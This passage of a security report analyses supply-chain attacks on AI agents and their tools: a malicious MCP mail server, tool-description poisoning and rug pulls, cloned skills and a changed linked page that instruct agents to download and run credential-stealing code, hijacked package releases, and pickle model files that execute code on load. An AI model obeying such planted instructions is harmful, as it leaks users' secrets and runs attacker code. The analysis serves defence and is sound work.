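A new release of the mailbox server is one such change for the invented shop. If the shop also tracks parcels through a courier's remote MCP server, the courier can change the tool descriptions or the code behind them after the shop's developer has read the descriptions. If the `refund-replies` skill tells the agent to read the latest refund rules on a web page, the page's owner can edit it.

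A pin or a hash protects the shop to a different extent in each case:

| What changes | What a pin or hash covers | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| A package gets a new release | The release the shop approved | Anything already wrong with that release |
| A remote server changes | The tool descriptions, if the application stored them at approval | What the server does with each call, and what it returns |
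| A page that a skill links to changes | The skill's own files | The page |

### The postmark-mcp package

Postmark, an email-sending service for companies, kept an official MCP server on GitHub. Postmark later said it had never published the server on npm. Somebody else copied the code and uploaded it to npm as `postmark-mcp` on 15 September 2025. Two days later the same publisher released version 1.0.16, which added one line that sent a hidden copy of every outgoing email to the publisher's address. Koi, which discovered the line, called the package the first malicious MCP server found in real use.

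The agent could not have detected the hidden recipient. Its model called the "send" tool with a recipient, a subject and a text, and the server then added the hidden recipient and reported success. A person approving the call would have seen only what the model wrote. According to Koi, nothing else changed in that version, so the tool would also have passed a check of its description.

Koi and Postmark interpret the earlier versions differently. Koi describes a developer with a real name and a respectable GitHub profile who behaved well for 15 versions and then betrayed the users. Postmark describes an impostor who used those versions to build trust. The dates fit Postmark's account better, because Snyk found that every version from 1.0.0 to 1.0.18 appeared between 15 and 17 September, so the package's good record lasted about two days. A high version number is poor evidence that anyone has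 used a package for long, since honest developers also release many small fixes in a project's first days.

Operators who had pinned one of the early versions were safe, but anyone who first installed the package on 18 September and pinned the newest version got the malicious code. The three-day cooldown that would have kept out both LiteLLM attacks would probably have been too short here, since version 1.0.16 would have become eligible on 20 September and Snyk first records the package as missing from npm on 25 September. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), the package's entry in a public database that security tools consult, dates from 26 September, nine days after the malicious release.

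When Koi asked the publisher for an explanation, the publisher deleted the package without replying. This stopped new installations, but copies already installed kept sending out their users' mail.

The Hacker News (2025) gives 1,643 as the package's total number of downloads. The much larger numbers in circulation come from Koi's estimate of the stolen mail, which goes like this:

```
1,500 downloads a week × 20% in active use = 300 organisations
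300 organisations × 10 to 50 emails a day  = 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day
```

Koi acknowledges that the 20% and the 10 to 50 emails are guesses. The calculation also treats every active download as a separate organisation, so a machine that fetched three versions would count three times. If all 19 version numbers were published, the 1,643 downloads come to about 86 per version. Some of the downloads were of clean versions, and some probably went to mirrors and security scanners. The number of stolen emails is unknown, and Koi's range is probably too high.

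### Tool descriptions that change

In tool poisoning, an attacker hides instructions for the model in a tool's description. Acharya and Gupta cite a demonstration by Invariant Labs where a "Fact of the Day" tool could get an agent to send out a user's entire WhatsApp history. A user who read that description carefully would refuse the tool. In a rug pull, the server shows the user a harmless description, waits for approval, and then replaces it.

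Acharya and Gupta list two less obvious variants. A server can revert to an older version with a known flaw, which a check of the newer version would not catch. Or it can expand what a tool does a little in each session, so that no single change looks alarming.

The Model Context Protocol makes it easy for servers to change their tools because legitimate servers need to do so. An application requests the list of tools when it connects, so the descriptions can change with each new session. In the protocol's 2025 versions, a server could also notify the application during a session that the list had changed, and the application could then request it again. A server might do this after the user signs in and gains access to more tools.

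Those versions did not require the application to show the user the new text or ask for approval again. The application also could not rely on the announcement as a warning, since a malicious server could withhold it. Servers reported a version number, but each server's owner chose it and could leave it unchanged.

The effect of a change therefore depends on what the application stores when the user approves a tool. An application that stores only the approval of a tool called `send_email` will apply it to whatever description that tool has next, while one that stores the approved text can detect the difference. Operators can check which kind they have by running a small test server, approving its tool, changing the description and reconnecting.

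There is little evidence on how often rug pulls succeed. Acharya and Gupta compared three MCP benchmarks and write that none covers these attacks, although in their table they give one, MCPSecBench, partial credit for changes made after approval.

### Signed and versioned tool definitions

An application can protect its users from altered descriptions without any help from the server's publisher:

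`offer tool to model only if hash(name, description, input format) = hash recorded at approval`

This rule detects every change in the text, including a return to an older version, but it doesn't identify who made the change. Several proposals therefore add signatures. Acharya and Gupta describe one called ETDI, which ties each tool definition to a verified identity using OAuth, a widely used standard for granting access. Another, MCPS, signs the messages between application and server. Jamshidi and colleagues propose signing the file that lists a server's tools, called a manifest, and using a second language model to check the tool descriptions for hidden instructions.

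If definitions also carry version numbers, the publisher has to give each changed definition a new number and sign it. The application rejects anything without a valid signature and asks the user before accepting a new version. It also has to remember the newest version it has accepted so that it can reject older ones, because the signature on an old, flawed version remains valid.

The extra work falls mostly on honest publishers and their users. Publishers have to protect a signing key and use it for every correction, and applications need a reliable way to learn which key belongs to whom. Users get a prompt whenever somebody fixes a typo. The shop's developer might read the first few prompts and approve the rest without looking, which would leave the shop no safer than before. Showing only the changed words would help. The application should compare the new text with what the user originally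 read, because comparing it with last week's version would hide a gradual expansion.

A strict comparison also breaks servers that have good reasons to describe their tools differently to different users. Having a second model read the descriptions avoids some of the prompts, but it adds time and expense, and the attacker's text may mislead that model too.

Even if everyone accepted these drawbacks, the signatures would cover only a server's descriptions of its tools. The postmark-mcp server would have passed the signature check, because its publisher changed the code but not the description. Checking a hash of the package detects such a change in a local server, but with a remote server the operator can only limit the data it receives. For example, the courier's server needs a parcel number but not the customer's whole email.

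Acharya and Gupta calculate that no existing defence covers more than 34% of the 23 attack types they list, and that their own design, which combines four kinds of defence, would cover 91%. They call the 91% figure theoretical. It is the share of attack types that the design addresses on paper, and doesn't measure how many attacks the design would stop.

### The cloned skills on skills.sh

Skills can also gain a reputation while they are harmless and become malicious later. Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain* describes a criminal campaign that did this in July 2026. On 2 July an attacker copied the entire repository of Paperclip, a popular AI tool, including its set of useful skills, into a GitHub organisation with a similar name. By 5 July skills.sh listed the copied skills, and their files were still identical to the originals.

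On 11 July the attacker added the same setup document in seven places in the repository. The document contained instructions for agents to download a program from the attacker's server and run it. The program searched more than 100 locations for SSH keys, cloud credentials, package-publishing tokens and other secrets, and sent the attacker whatever it found.

Agents load skills in stages, which helped to hide the command. The main skill files described ordinary tasks and directed the agent to the setup document only if Paperclip was missing or needed starting. Several skills referred the agent to the main `paperclip` skill, which referred it to the setup document. A reviewer who read only the main file of one of those skills would not have found the command. The setup document also called the attacker's copy the only supported way to install Paperclip and warned agents not to use the genuine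 npm package.

The malicious skills remained available for 22 days and kept appearing on the site's trending list. Zenity noticed them late on 1 August. GitHub and Vercel, the company behind skills.sh, removed them within 12 hours of Zenity's report.

Defenders caught the same attacker much faster on PyPI. One malicious Python package, published on 13 July, was public for less than two hours before they identified it, compared with three weeks for the skills. They identified a second package within an hour on 20 July. Both contained variants of the same credential-stealing program. The difference is partly because the packages contained their malicious code, where a scanner could find it, while the skills contained only instructions for fetching it. Many companies also check new PyPI packages. One attacker's experience doesn't show how well either registry is monitored in general.

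By 2 August the counters on the Paperclip skills added up to more than 1.7 million installs. Zenity Labs warns that these are not unique users, and its figures for 11 July suggest how much double-counting there was. On that day the leading skill showed 7,800 installs and all six skills together showed 46,600, an average of about 7,770. Six separate skills would hardly attract such similar numbers unless people were installing them as a set, with each installation counted six times:

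```
1,700,000 installs ÷ 6 skills ≈ 283,000 installs of the set
```

This fits the counts of nearly 300,000 that Zenity saw on individual skills. Even 283,000 would include repeat installs by the same user, and some installs may have been fake. One of the skills already showed 2,264 installs on the first day for which Zenity found records, three days after the attacker made the copy.

The number of infections is smaller still, because an agent had to open and follow the setup document, or the user had to install or run the attacker's version of Paperclip. Zenity doesn't know how many victims there were.

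A hash would have helped some users. Anyone who installed a skill before 11 July and kept that copy had clean files. If they later updated it, the new document would have changed a hash of the whole folder, though possibly not a hash of SKILL.md alone. For anyone who first approved the skill after 11 July, the hash would have kept matching even if the attacker repeatedly replaced the program on the server, because that would not require changing any file in the skill.

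### A linked page that changed after review

In a June 2026 demonstration on real users, the security company AIR tested how far a skill could get if nothing in its own files was malicious. AIR published its account, *The Story of Skills*, on 22 June. In *Anatomy of a Malicious AI Skill*, Hoppe (2026) checked parts of that account against the public record on GitHub.

AIR presented its skill, `brand-landingpage`, as a way to interview users about their brand and build them a web page with Stitch, a Google design tool. The Hacker News (2026) reports that AIR submitted it to a GitHub repository with 156 skills and about 36,000 stars. The maintainers accepted it after a few days. The skill then appeared to have 36,000 stars, although people had given them to the collection as a whole. AIR also bought an Instagram advertisement aimed at marketers, salespeople and designers.

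The skill told the agent to read the documentation for Stitch's software kit, treat it as the "ground truth", install the kit if it was missing, and avoid bothering the user with technical details. Hoppe points out that an honest author could write all of this for a new and fast-changing tool. The only thing wrong was that AIR owned the documentation's address. The link first led to the genuine Stitch documentation, but after enough people had installed the skill, AIR replaced the page with one that told agents to download and run a script.

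Every scanner that AIR tried, including Cisco's, NVIDIA's and those built into skills.sh, had rated the skill safe. They examined the submitted files, which never changed. Pinning the skill would have failed for the same reason. Even if the shop had recorded the exact commit and a hash of every file in the folder, both would still have matched on the day the script ran.

AIR's script only sent the user's email address to the company. From these messages, AIR counted about 26,000 agents, some of them on corporate accounts. This is a better measure than an install counter because it records that the script ran. But only AIR has the data. The Hacker News notes that nobody has independently confirmed the figure, and doesn't report whether AIR removed duplicates, such as one person running the skill on two computers.

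AIR had a commercial reason to publish a large number. The company dates from February 2026 and has raised $50 million, according to CTech, to secure the supply chain of AI agents. Niv Hoffman, its co-founder and technology chief, co-wrote the report, which ends by promoting AIR's managed marketplace for skills. This casts little doubt on the method, which doesn't depend on how many people installed the skill. Anyone can read the skill's file, which was still on GitHub when Hoppe wrote about it in September, and see that it sends agents to an address outside Google.

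AIR also counted more than 17,800 public add-ons, with 6.7 million installations, that take instructions from unverified outside sources, according to SiliconANGLE. Jones's *Agent Skills* put the totals in October 2026 at over 1 million published skills and nearly 280 million installations. If AIR's add-ons were all skills, they would make up roughly 2% of each total. Most are presumably legitimate, since it is normal for a skill to link to current documentation, but whoever controls the linked page can use it to instruct agents that have already approved the skill.

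The shop could try extending its hash rule to the page:

`follow page only if hash(page as the agent received it) = hash recorded at approval`

This would have stopped AIR's script, but it would also stop the agent whenever the page's owner corrected a sentence and, on many sites, whenever a date or a menu changed. A more practical fix is to copy the needed text into the skill's folder, delete the link, and approve the folder as a whole, so that an ordinary hash covers everything the skill asks the agent to read. The copy will gradually go out of date, and AIR chose a subject that made this a plausible reason to read the live page instead. The reason given in the skill was that the software was new and still changing.

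## Hijacked publishers, and what hashes, signatures and provenance prove

Even if the shop pins every package and keeps its skills' reference pages in its own folder, it sometimes has to accept new versions, if only to get security fixes. Its recorded hashes can't help it decide whether to accept one, because a legitimate update changes a file's hash just as a malicious one does. The shop needs evidence that the new file comes from the real publisher, which is hardest to get when an attacker has taken over the publisher's account or release process.

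### Two malicious releases of Microsoft's agent-framework

Agent Framework is Microsoft's open-source toolkit for building agents. Python developers install it from PyPI as the package agent-framework. On 17 November 2026, somebody uploaded two malicious versions to the genuine PyPI project. The times below combine Read's (2026) analysis for the security company Wiz, *Microsoft agent-framework Compromised*, with the intervals in TechRadar's *Microsoft's official Agent Framework Python package on PyPI hijacked*.

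| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 12 November, 18:25 | Microsoft publishes 1.26.0, the last clean version |
| 17 November, 20:35 | The attacker uploads 1.26.1 |
| About 21:06 | PyPI quarantines 1.26.1 |
| About 21:08 | The attacker uploads 1.26.2 |
| About 21:16 | PyPI removes 1.26.2 |

PyPI's response was fast, but the quarantine blocked only the release and left the attacker able to publish another one two minutes later.

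Both versions installed the genuine core of the framework, so agents built with it kept working. As in the LiteLLM attack, a start-up file ran the malware whenever Python started. According to Read, the malware searched the environments of up to 300 other processes for secrets, copied credential files, and requested new access tokens from Azure, Microsoft's cloud. Version 1.26.2 also requested tokens from GitHub's build system. It used different file names, so an operator who searched only for the 1.26.1 names would miss it.

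TechRadar reported that the attackers had spread the malware to "hundreds of thousands of developers" who rely on the package daily. The article's own figure of about 6,900 downloads a day rules that out. It also estimates that users downloaded the malicious versions about 150 times, which seems to count only the 31 minutes when 1.26.1 was available:

```
287 downloads an hour × 31/60 ≈ 148   (1.26.1 only)
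287 downloads an hour × 39/60 ≈ 187   (both versions)
```

Both results assume that every download was the newest version. For LiteLLM, PyPI estimated that slightly under half were. Downloads by mirrors and security scanners would also inflate the number.

The attacker's choice of collection point gives a firmer limit. The malware sent the stolen secrets to a free public service that logs at most 100 web requests per address, so at most 100 machines can have delivered their secrets. The true number is probably lower, because one machine could send several requests and some will have come from researchers' test systems. Read confirmed that the service had captured at most 50 requests, but if that count dates from the day of the attack, infected machines could have added to it later, since the malware ran every time Python started. Even a single request from a build server could contain the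 keys to a company's whole cloud.

Nobody has publicly explained how the attacker got the right to publish. Help Net Security's *Credential stealer slipped into Microsoft’s official Python agent framework* notes that none of the security companies' reports explain it. Microsoft's statement of 25 November, *Microsoft Agent Framework repository update* (Taylor, 2026), doesn't either. It says the malicious code was only in the published packages and never in the GitHub repository. Microsoft still took the repository offline as a precaution and reopened it on 30 November, according to Eurasia Review's *AI Writes The Code, Who Controls The Update?* The closure might mean that Microsoft suspected the project's release process, but a cautious company would also close the repository while it didn't know how the attacker had gained access.

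Read's evidence suggests that the attacker built version 1.26.1 elsewhere and uploaded it directly. The GitHub repository had no matching tag or release. Microsoft normally publishes a ready-to-install file and a source archive, along with a core package of the same version number. But 1.26.1 came as a single file that depended on the 1.26.0 core.

The same thing had happened in May to durabletask, another Microsoft package. StepSecurity, a company that monitors build systems, reports that three malicious versions appeared on PyPI within 35 minutes, again with no matching tags, releases or build runs. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-207* (2026) attributes them to a compromised maintainer account. Read mentions the case but has found no link between the two attacks.

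A person who compared either package with its GitHub page could have seen that something was wrong, but installers don't compare them, so the evidence must be something software can check.

### Hashes

A hash check compares two numbers, and what it proves depends on where the expected number came from.

PyPI lists a hash for every file, which an installer can use to detect a file damaged in transit or altered on a mirror (a copy of the registry that somebody else runs). The hash couldn't have exposed version 1.26.1, because PyPI computes it from whatever the uploader sends, so the malicious file matched its listed hash.

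The hash in a lock file is better evidence because it was recorded earlier. It proves that today's file is the one the installer selected when the developer last updated the lock file. A project locked to agent-framework 1.26.0 stayed clean throughout. As with LiteLLM, an update while the malicious file was on PyPI would have put that file's hash in the lock file. Once PyPI removed the file, later installs from PyPI would fail, but a company mirror or a local cache could still supply a copy that passed the check. Taylor therefore tells users to search mirrors, caches and container images as well as their machines.

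### Signatures and Sigstore

To sign a file, a publisher computes its hash and processes the hash with a private key. Anyone who has the matching public key can then verify the signature. The rule has two conditions:

`accept file only if signature is valid and signer = expected publisher`

Without the second condition the rule is nearly worthless, because an attacker can make a valid signature with the attacker's own key.

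A registry may also sign packages itself. Nesbitt (2026) points out in *Signing and Attestations Across Package Registries* that a registry's signature shows only that a file matches what somebody uploaded. It exposes a tampered mirror, but a release that a thief uploads with a stolen token gets the same signature as a genuine one. Linux distributions such as Debian also sign their packages centrally, but their signatures show more. Debian builds each package on its own machines from source code submitted by a vetted group of packagers, while PyPI and npm accept finished files from anyone with an account.

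PyPI let authors upload signatures made with PGP, an older signing tool, until May 2023. Before ending the feature, it examined 1,069 keys from the previous three years and could not find about 30% of them on the major public key servers. To verify signatures made with the missing keys, users would have had to get the keys some other way, and hardly anyone would have tried.

Sigstore, a free public service that both registries now use, avoids the problem by having signers throw their keys away:

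1. The signer creates a temporary key and proves an identity to Sigstore. The identity can be an email account or a particular GitHub workflow.
2. Sigstore issues a certificate that ties the key to that identity and expires after about ten minutes.
3. The signer signs the file's hash and discards the key.
4. Sigstore records the signing in a public log that accepts new entries but doesn't allow anyone to alter old ones.

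The verifier no longer needs to find a key, but does need to know which identity to expect. For the shop's mailbox server, this might be "the release workflow in `example-author/mailbox-mcp`". The signing key no longer exists, so a thief can't steal it, but a thief who takes over the email account or the workflow can still get a genuine certificate from Sigstore. The public log helps publishers who check it to detect this afterwards, since it lists every signature made in their name.

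### Provenance, SLSA and trusted publishing

A signature doesn't identify the source code from which somebody built the file. Provenance does. A provenance record for the invented mailbox server would contain roughly this, plus a signature:

```
file:        example-mailbox-mcp-2.3.1.tgz
hash:        <hash of that file>
repository:  example-author/mailbox-mcp
commit:      <ID of the source code used>
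workflow:    release.yml
```

The verifier checks the signature, compares the hash with the downloaded file, and compares the repository and workflow with the expected ones. Registries call these signed statements attestations.

How far to believe the record depends on who wrote it. SLSA (Supply-chain Levels for Software Artifacts) is a framework that grades builds by this:

| Build level | Requirement |
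|---|---|
| 1 | A provenance record exists, possibly without a signature |
| 2 | A hosted build service creates and signs the record |
| 3 | The service also prevents builds from influencing one another, and keeps the signing secrets away from the project's own build steps |

At level 1, a dishonest or hacked developer can write anything in the record. At level 2, the developer would have to deceive the build service, and level 3 is meant to make that very hard.

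The two main registries, npm and PyPI, offer different records. According to Nesbitt, npm attaches SLSA provenance, which includes the repository, commit and workflow. It has done so by default since July 2025 for packages released through Trusted Publishing. PyPI's usual attestation records which trusted publisher uploaded the file, but not the full details of the build. A PyPI user can therefore learn that a file came from the expected project's workflow, but may not learn exactly which source code went into it.

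Trusted Publishing, the system whose npm version had the flaw with recycled repository names, removes the kind of permanent token that was stolen from LiteLLM. But as Nesbitt puts it, the workflow's identity becomes the credential, so anyone who can run code inside the workflow can publish.

A project can have both weaknesses at once. In December 2024, attackers compromised Ultralytics, a Python package for image recognition. Nesbitt recounts that the first malicious releases came from the project's own release workflow and had valid attestations. The attackers then used a leaked token to upload more releases without attestations. The project had adopted the safer publishing method without disabling the old one. Investigators could still use the attestations to tell which releases came from the workflow and which were uploaded with the token.

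An installer could use the same difference to protect users before they install anything:

`reject update if the previous version had provenance and the new one has none`

pnpm, an alternative package manager for the npm registry, has an optional setting that works much like this. The rule needs no list of trusted identities, and it stops a thief who has only a token, provided the project's genuine releases always have provenance. On PyPI it could raise false alarms, because PyPI allows attestations to arrive after the file, so a genuine release might briefly lack one.

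If Microsoft had attested every genuine release of agent-framework, and users' installers had required that attestation, a direct upload of the kind Read describes would have failed. This requirement gives no protection against an attacker inside the release workflow.

### Malicious packages with valid provenance

Shai-Hulud is a family of npm worms that steal a developer's publishing credentials and use them to release infected versions of that developer's packages, which then infect other developers. Snyk lists a wave in September 2025 with more than 500 packages and another that November with 492. A smaller wave on 11 May 2026 involved 373 malicious versions of 169 packages. Snyk describes it as the first npm worm whose packages had valid SLSA level 3 provenance.

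The best-documented victim is TanStack, a group of libraries that many web developers use. InfoQ's *TanStack Details Sophisticated npm Supply Chain Attack That Compromised 42 Packages* (2026), which summarises the project's postmortem, reports that the attacker published 84 malicious versions in six minutes. A GitLab advisory adds that each package got two malicious versions, a few minutes apart.

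GitLab and InfoQ name the same three weaknesses, which the attacker combined as follows:

1. TanStack had a GitHub workflow that ran automatically when an outsider proposed a change to the code. Such a workflow should treat the outsider's code as hostile. This one ran it with access to resources of the main project.
2. One of those resources was the build cache, a store of files that later builds reuse to save time. The attacker put a poisoned entry in it.
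3. When a trusted workflow reused the entry, the attacker's code ran inside it. The code read the workflow's identity token from the build machine's memory and used it to publish to npm.

npm treated these as normal releases because the token was genuine and belonged to the right workflow in the right repository. The attacker didn't have to forge the provenance records, which correctly identified TanStack's pipeline as the source of the packages.

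StepSecurity found that the malicious TanStack packages had valid provenance. Infosecurity Magazine's *Mini Shai-Hulud Hits TanStack npm Packages* quotes the company as saying that SLSA provenance "confirms which pipeline produced the artifact". The TanStack packages account for only 84 of the 373 malicious versions in Snyk's list, or about 23%, so we can't assume that all 373 had valid provenance.

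Snyk also writes that no earlier supply-chain attack had produced malicious packages that provenance couldn't distinguish from legitimate ones. But the first malicious Ultralytics releases had done much the same on PyPI 17 months earlier, although with PyPI's narrower kind of attestation. The May attack was new in combining this with a worm and with npm's fuller build records.

SLSA's Level 3 requirements forbid one build from planting false entries in a cache that another build uses. The attacker got in through a poisoned cache, so the TanStack build did not meet Level 3. But a provenance record doesn't contain a measured level. The verifier looks up which build service signed the record and assumes the level that the service can achieve when a project uses it properly, so a project that uses a strong service carelessly is given the same level as one that uses it carefully.

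A stronger check would be for somebody independent to build the package again from the commit named in the provenance:

`hash(package rebuilt from the named commit) = hash(published package)`

The malicious TanStack packages contained a new 2.3 MB file of disguised code, according to the security company Socket. If that file came from the poisoned cache and not from the project's source code, a clean rebuild would have lacked it and the hashes would have differed. But many projects don't produce identical files from identical source code, because their builds include things like the current time. The rebuilding also costs money. Against a fast-moving attack, a cooldown of a few days is cheaper and probably more effective.

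The agent-framework malware requested fresh identity tokens from Azure and GitHub, much as the TanStack attacker used the one in the build machine's memory. StepSecurity, quoted by Help Net Security, warns that changing stored passwords doesn't cancel tokens a cloud service has already issued, but adds that nobody has confirmed that any of the requests succeeded. Victims should also review which workflows and machines their cloud accounts trust, and rebuild the affected environments from a clean image, because downgrading to 1.26.0 would remove the package but might leave other changes behind.

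### Tampered releases of two coding agents

Attackers have used both routes, the source repository and the stolen token, against agents themselves.

In July 2025 an attacker got malicious code into the GitHub repository of Amazon Q's extension for the code editor Visual Studio Code. Amazon later blamed the breach on a GitHub token with excessive permissions in its build configuration. The code contained instructions for the agent to delete the user's files and cloud resources. Amazon included it in version 1.84.0 of the extension, but a syntax error kept it from running. Amazon replaced that release with 1.85.0.

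This version would have passed every check described so far. The publisher was Amazon, a signature by Amazon would have been genuine, and provenance would have led back to Amazon's repository. An independent rebuild would also have matched, because the harmful text was already in the source. Stopping the release required someone to read the change beforehand and object to it.

On 17 February 2026, somebody used a stolen npm token to publish version 2.3.0 of the command-line tool for Cline, another coding agent. The only harmful addition was an installation step that put OpenClaw on the user's machine. OpenClaw isn't malware, but it is an agent with wide permissions, and these users had not chosen to install it. The release stayed up for about eight hours and had around 4,000 downloads.

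A week earlier, the researcher Adnan Khan had published a way to steal Cline's publishing tokens. Cline used an AI agent to sort incoming GitHub issues, and an outsider could give that agent instructions in an issue's title. From there, an attacker could poison the build cache and reach the release credentials, as in the TanStack attack three months later. Those credentials would have let the attacker publish a malicious package to Cline's users. After the incident, Cline moved its npm releases to Trusted Publishing. That removes the kind of token the thief used, but an attacker who got into the release workflow itself could still publish.

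### Whether anyone checks

Attestations protect only users whose software verifies them, and only for packages that have them. PyPI reported that 17% of all uploads in 2025 included one. A company that refused packages without attestations would have to do without most of PyPI, including many legitimate packages whose maintainers release them by hand.

Maintainers have reasons for not adopting provenance. Nesbitt cites a study of 1,523 GitHub issues about SLSA, in which the main obstacles to adoption were complex implementation and unclear communication. npm issues provenance only for packages built on certain hosted services, so a maintainer who builds on private machines can't get it.

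Verification is also often a separate step. On npm, a developer can run `npm audit signatures` to check a project's packages. RubyGems, the registry for the Ruby language, has an older signature scheme that its installer checks only if the user adds an option. Developers who don't know about these checks get no warning that they have skipped them.

Registries have tried to make the records easier to read. The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), an industry body, funded interviews with maintainers, security researchers and ordinary package users, described in its *Clearer Security Signals* (2026). Specialists generally knew what to look for, but less experienced users often lacked the background to interpret the technical details. Most users cared more about whether a package was useful than whether it was secure. PyPI has since redesigned its project pages based on the findings. Pogorelec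 (2026), in *PyPI makes release attestations easier to find with new security tab*, reports that the new pages include warnings about provenance.

A clearer page helps a developer who is choosing a package, but a launcher such as `uvx` never opens it. For agents, the check has to happen in the installer or in a company mirror that stands between the agent and the public registry. The mirror's owner can write down the expected source of each package once:

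```
package:     example-mailbox-mcp
repository:  example-author/mailbox-mcp
workflow:    release.yml
if missing or different: block and ask a person
```

The list takes work to maintain. Projects move to new repositories and rename their workflows, and each change would block a legitimate update until someone reviewed it. Most small teams won't keep up such a list for 77 packages, the number that `uvx` installed on McMahon's laptop for one tool server. They could reasonably do it for the few packages that handle credentials, and rely on lock files and cooldowns for the rest.

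### Signing models

A model needs a slightly different kind of signature because it consists of many files. If ExampleLab signed only the weights of `support-8b`, an attacker could leave them alone and change the configuration or the tokenizer. OpenSSF's model-signing specification therefore has the publisher sign a list of all the files with their hashes:

```
config.json         <hash>
model.safetensors   <hash>
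tokenizer.json      <hash>
```

The verifier recomputes every hash, compares the results with the list, and checks the list's signature and the signer's identity. The check fails if a file is missing or altered, and it should also fail if there is an extra file. Publishers can sign through Sigstore or with their own keys. The signature is a separate file that anyone can copy along with the model.

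This would help prevent the takeover of deleted namespaces, because a stranger who registers `ExampleLab` can't sign as the laboratory. The shop would have to know beforehand which identity to expect, and its loading software would have to reject anything unsigned. Hugging Face doesn't require publishers to sign, so this rule would exclude a large part of the hub.

The laboratory's signature also doesn't match the converted copies of a model that volunteers publish, because conversion changes the bytes. A volunteer can sign the new files, but that signature would show only who made the conversion, not whether it is faithful to the original. A signed record of the conversion, with the model's hashes before and after, would give the user some evidence of faithfulness if they trusted whoever ran the conversion.

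A model's signature also provides no information about how the model behaves. If ExampleLab unknowingly trained a model on poisoned data, it would still sign the model.

### A model replaced during upload

A model can also change in transit from its owner to the service that runs it. In *Pickle in the Middle*, Hadad (2026) demonstrated this for Unit 42 on Google's Vertex AI.

To run a model on Vertex AI, a customer uploads it with Google's software kit for Python. The kit copies the model to a bucket, a named storage area in Google's cloud, and Vertex AI reads it from there. If the customer hadn't chosen a bucket, the kit computed a default name from the customer's project ID and region. Bucket names are unique across Google's cloud, and anyone can create a bucket with an unused name.

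The kit checked whether the default bucket existed but not who owned it. An attacker who knew the project ID, which is often public, could create the bucket first and open it to other accounts. The customer's kit would find a bucket with the right name and upload the model into the attacker's storage. In Hadad's tests, Vertex AI read the file about 2.5 seconds after the upload. An automatic program in the attacker's account reacted in about 0.8 seconds, which left enough time to swap the model. When Vertex AI loaded the replacement, code inside it ran and sent out the credentials of the machine running the model.

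The attack worked only if the customer had no default bucket in that region yet and hadn't specified another. The flaw affected versions 1.139.0 and 1.140.0 of the kit, and Google completed its fix in version 1.148.0, released on 15 April 2026. Hadad carried out the attack only as a demonstration and reported the flaw to Google before publishing.

The most direct remedy is for the kit to check that the bucket belongs to the customer, which it did not do. Customers could also protect themselves by specifying their own bucket. Scanning the model before upload would have found nothing, because the customer's file was clean.

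An integrity check would have caught the swap too, if it ran in the right place:

`load model only if hash(file about to load) = hash computed before upload`

The customer has to compute the expected hash on the machine where the model came from, because even a few seconds later the file in the bucket might already be the attacker's. The customer also can't simply store the expected hash in the same bucket, where the attacker could replace it along with the model. A signature can be stored there, because the attacker can't sign as the customer.

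The software that loads the model then has to verify its own copy of the file, once no one else can change it. A check at the start of the upload would pass but would miss any later change. Customers who supply their own serving software could build the check into it. Those who use Google's ready-made software, as the customer in Hadad's demonstration did, would need Google to add it.

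## Code that runs when a model is loaded or a project is opened

The replacement model in Hadad's Vertex AI demonstration could steal credentials because loading it ran code. A model is mostly numbers, but software has to rebuild it in memory before using it, and some file formats let the publisher choose which functions run during loading. Project folders create a similar risk for coding agents, because a settings file in the folder can start a program before the developer types anything.

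### Pickle files as lists of instructions

Pickle is Python's built-in way to save an object to a file and rebuild it later. A pickle file is a list of instructions, which Python carries out in order when somebody loads the file. Put into words, part of an ordinary model file might look like this:

```
find the function rebuild_tensor in the PyTorch library
prepare its arguments: these numbers, in this shape
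call the function with those arguments
store the result as the model's first layer
```

*PickleBall* (Kellas, Li and colleagues, 2025) explains why the pickle format is so permissive. Programmers save many kinds of object, so pickle lets each kind specify a function that will rebuild it. Python writes the function's name and arguments into the file, then imports and calls the function when the file is loaded. An attacker can substitute a different function, such as the one in Python's standard library that runs a shell command. The remaining instructions can still produce a working model, so the user may see nothing wrong.

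If the invented shop's `support-8b` were a malicious pickle file, the attacker's code would run with the permissions of whatever process loaded the model, before the agent answered any email. Testing the model's answers first wouldn't prevent this, because the shop would have to load the model to test it.

Since version 2.6, the loader in PyTorch, the library behind most of these models, has by default rejected any pickle file that calls a function outside a short approved list. The restriction also blocks some legitimate models. Kellas and colleagues checked 1,426 popular repositories that offered only pickle files, and 219 (15.4%) contained at least one model that the restricted loader would reject.

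Some libraries deal with this by switching the restriction off. The text-processing library flair does so because its models need functions that aren't on PyTorch's list. A user who follows flair's documentation therefore gets the old, permissive behaviour without choosing it.

Kellas and colleagues built an alternative that analyzes a library's source code to identify the functions its models legitimately need, and allows only those. In their tests it stopped all 84 malicious models but also rejected about a fifth of the 252 harmless ones. A user in a hurry who gets an error from a harmless model is likely to look for the setting that turns the protection off.

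### What safetensors removes

Hugging Face released the safetensors format in September 2022. A safetensors file contains the model's arrays of numbers, the name and shape of each array, and optional text about the model. The format has no instruction for calling a function, so the software that reads the file only has to copy numbers into memory. Kellas and colleagues note that the format has been through independent security audits.

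A repository with a safetensors file may still contain the older pickle version, which publishers often keep for users with old software. In March 2025, repositories with both formats had 1.7 billion downloads a month. The shop can make its loading software insist on the safer file:

```python
model = AutoModelForCausalLM.from_pretrained(
    "ExampleLab/support-8b",
    revision="<full commit ID recorded at approval>",
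    use_safetensors=True,
    trust_remote_code=False,
)
```

With `use_safetensors=True`, loading fails if the repository has no safetensors weights, instead of falling back to pickle. The last line concerns code that comes with a model. Safetensors doesn't cover that code or the configuration files.

Converting an old model is risky too, because the converter has to load the pickle. HiddenLayer's *Hijacking Safetensors Conversion on Hugging Face* demonstrated this on Hugging Face's conversion service. An attacker could take over the service by submitting a malicious model, then propose changes to any repository on the site while posing as the official conversion bot. Anyone converting an untrusted pickle should use an isolated machine that holds no credentials.

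### How many models still use pickle

The most recent count comes from Qin, Li and colleagues (2026), in *DITTO*, who looked at popular Hugging Face repositories created in the year to June 2026. It gives a much lower figure than the earlier study by Kellas and colleagues:

| | Kellas and colleagues | Qin and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Repositories | 16,661 of any age, in March 2025 | 10,023 created from July 2025 to June 2026 |
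| Monthly downloads | At least 1,000 | More than 1,000 |
| How they identified pickle | File extensions | Hugging Face's scan results, or their own checks |
| Share with pickle files | 44.9% | 9.3% |

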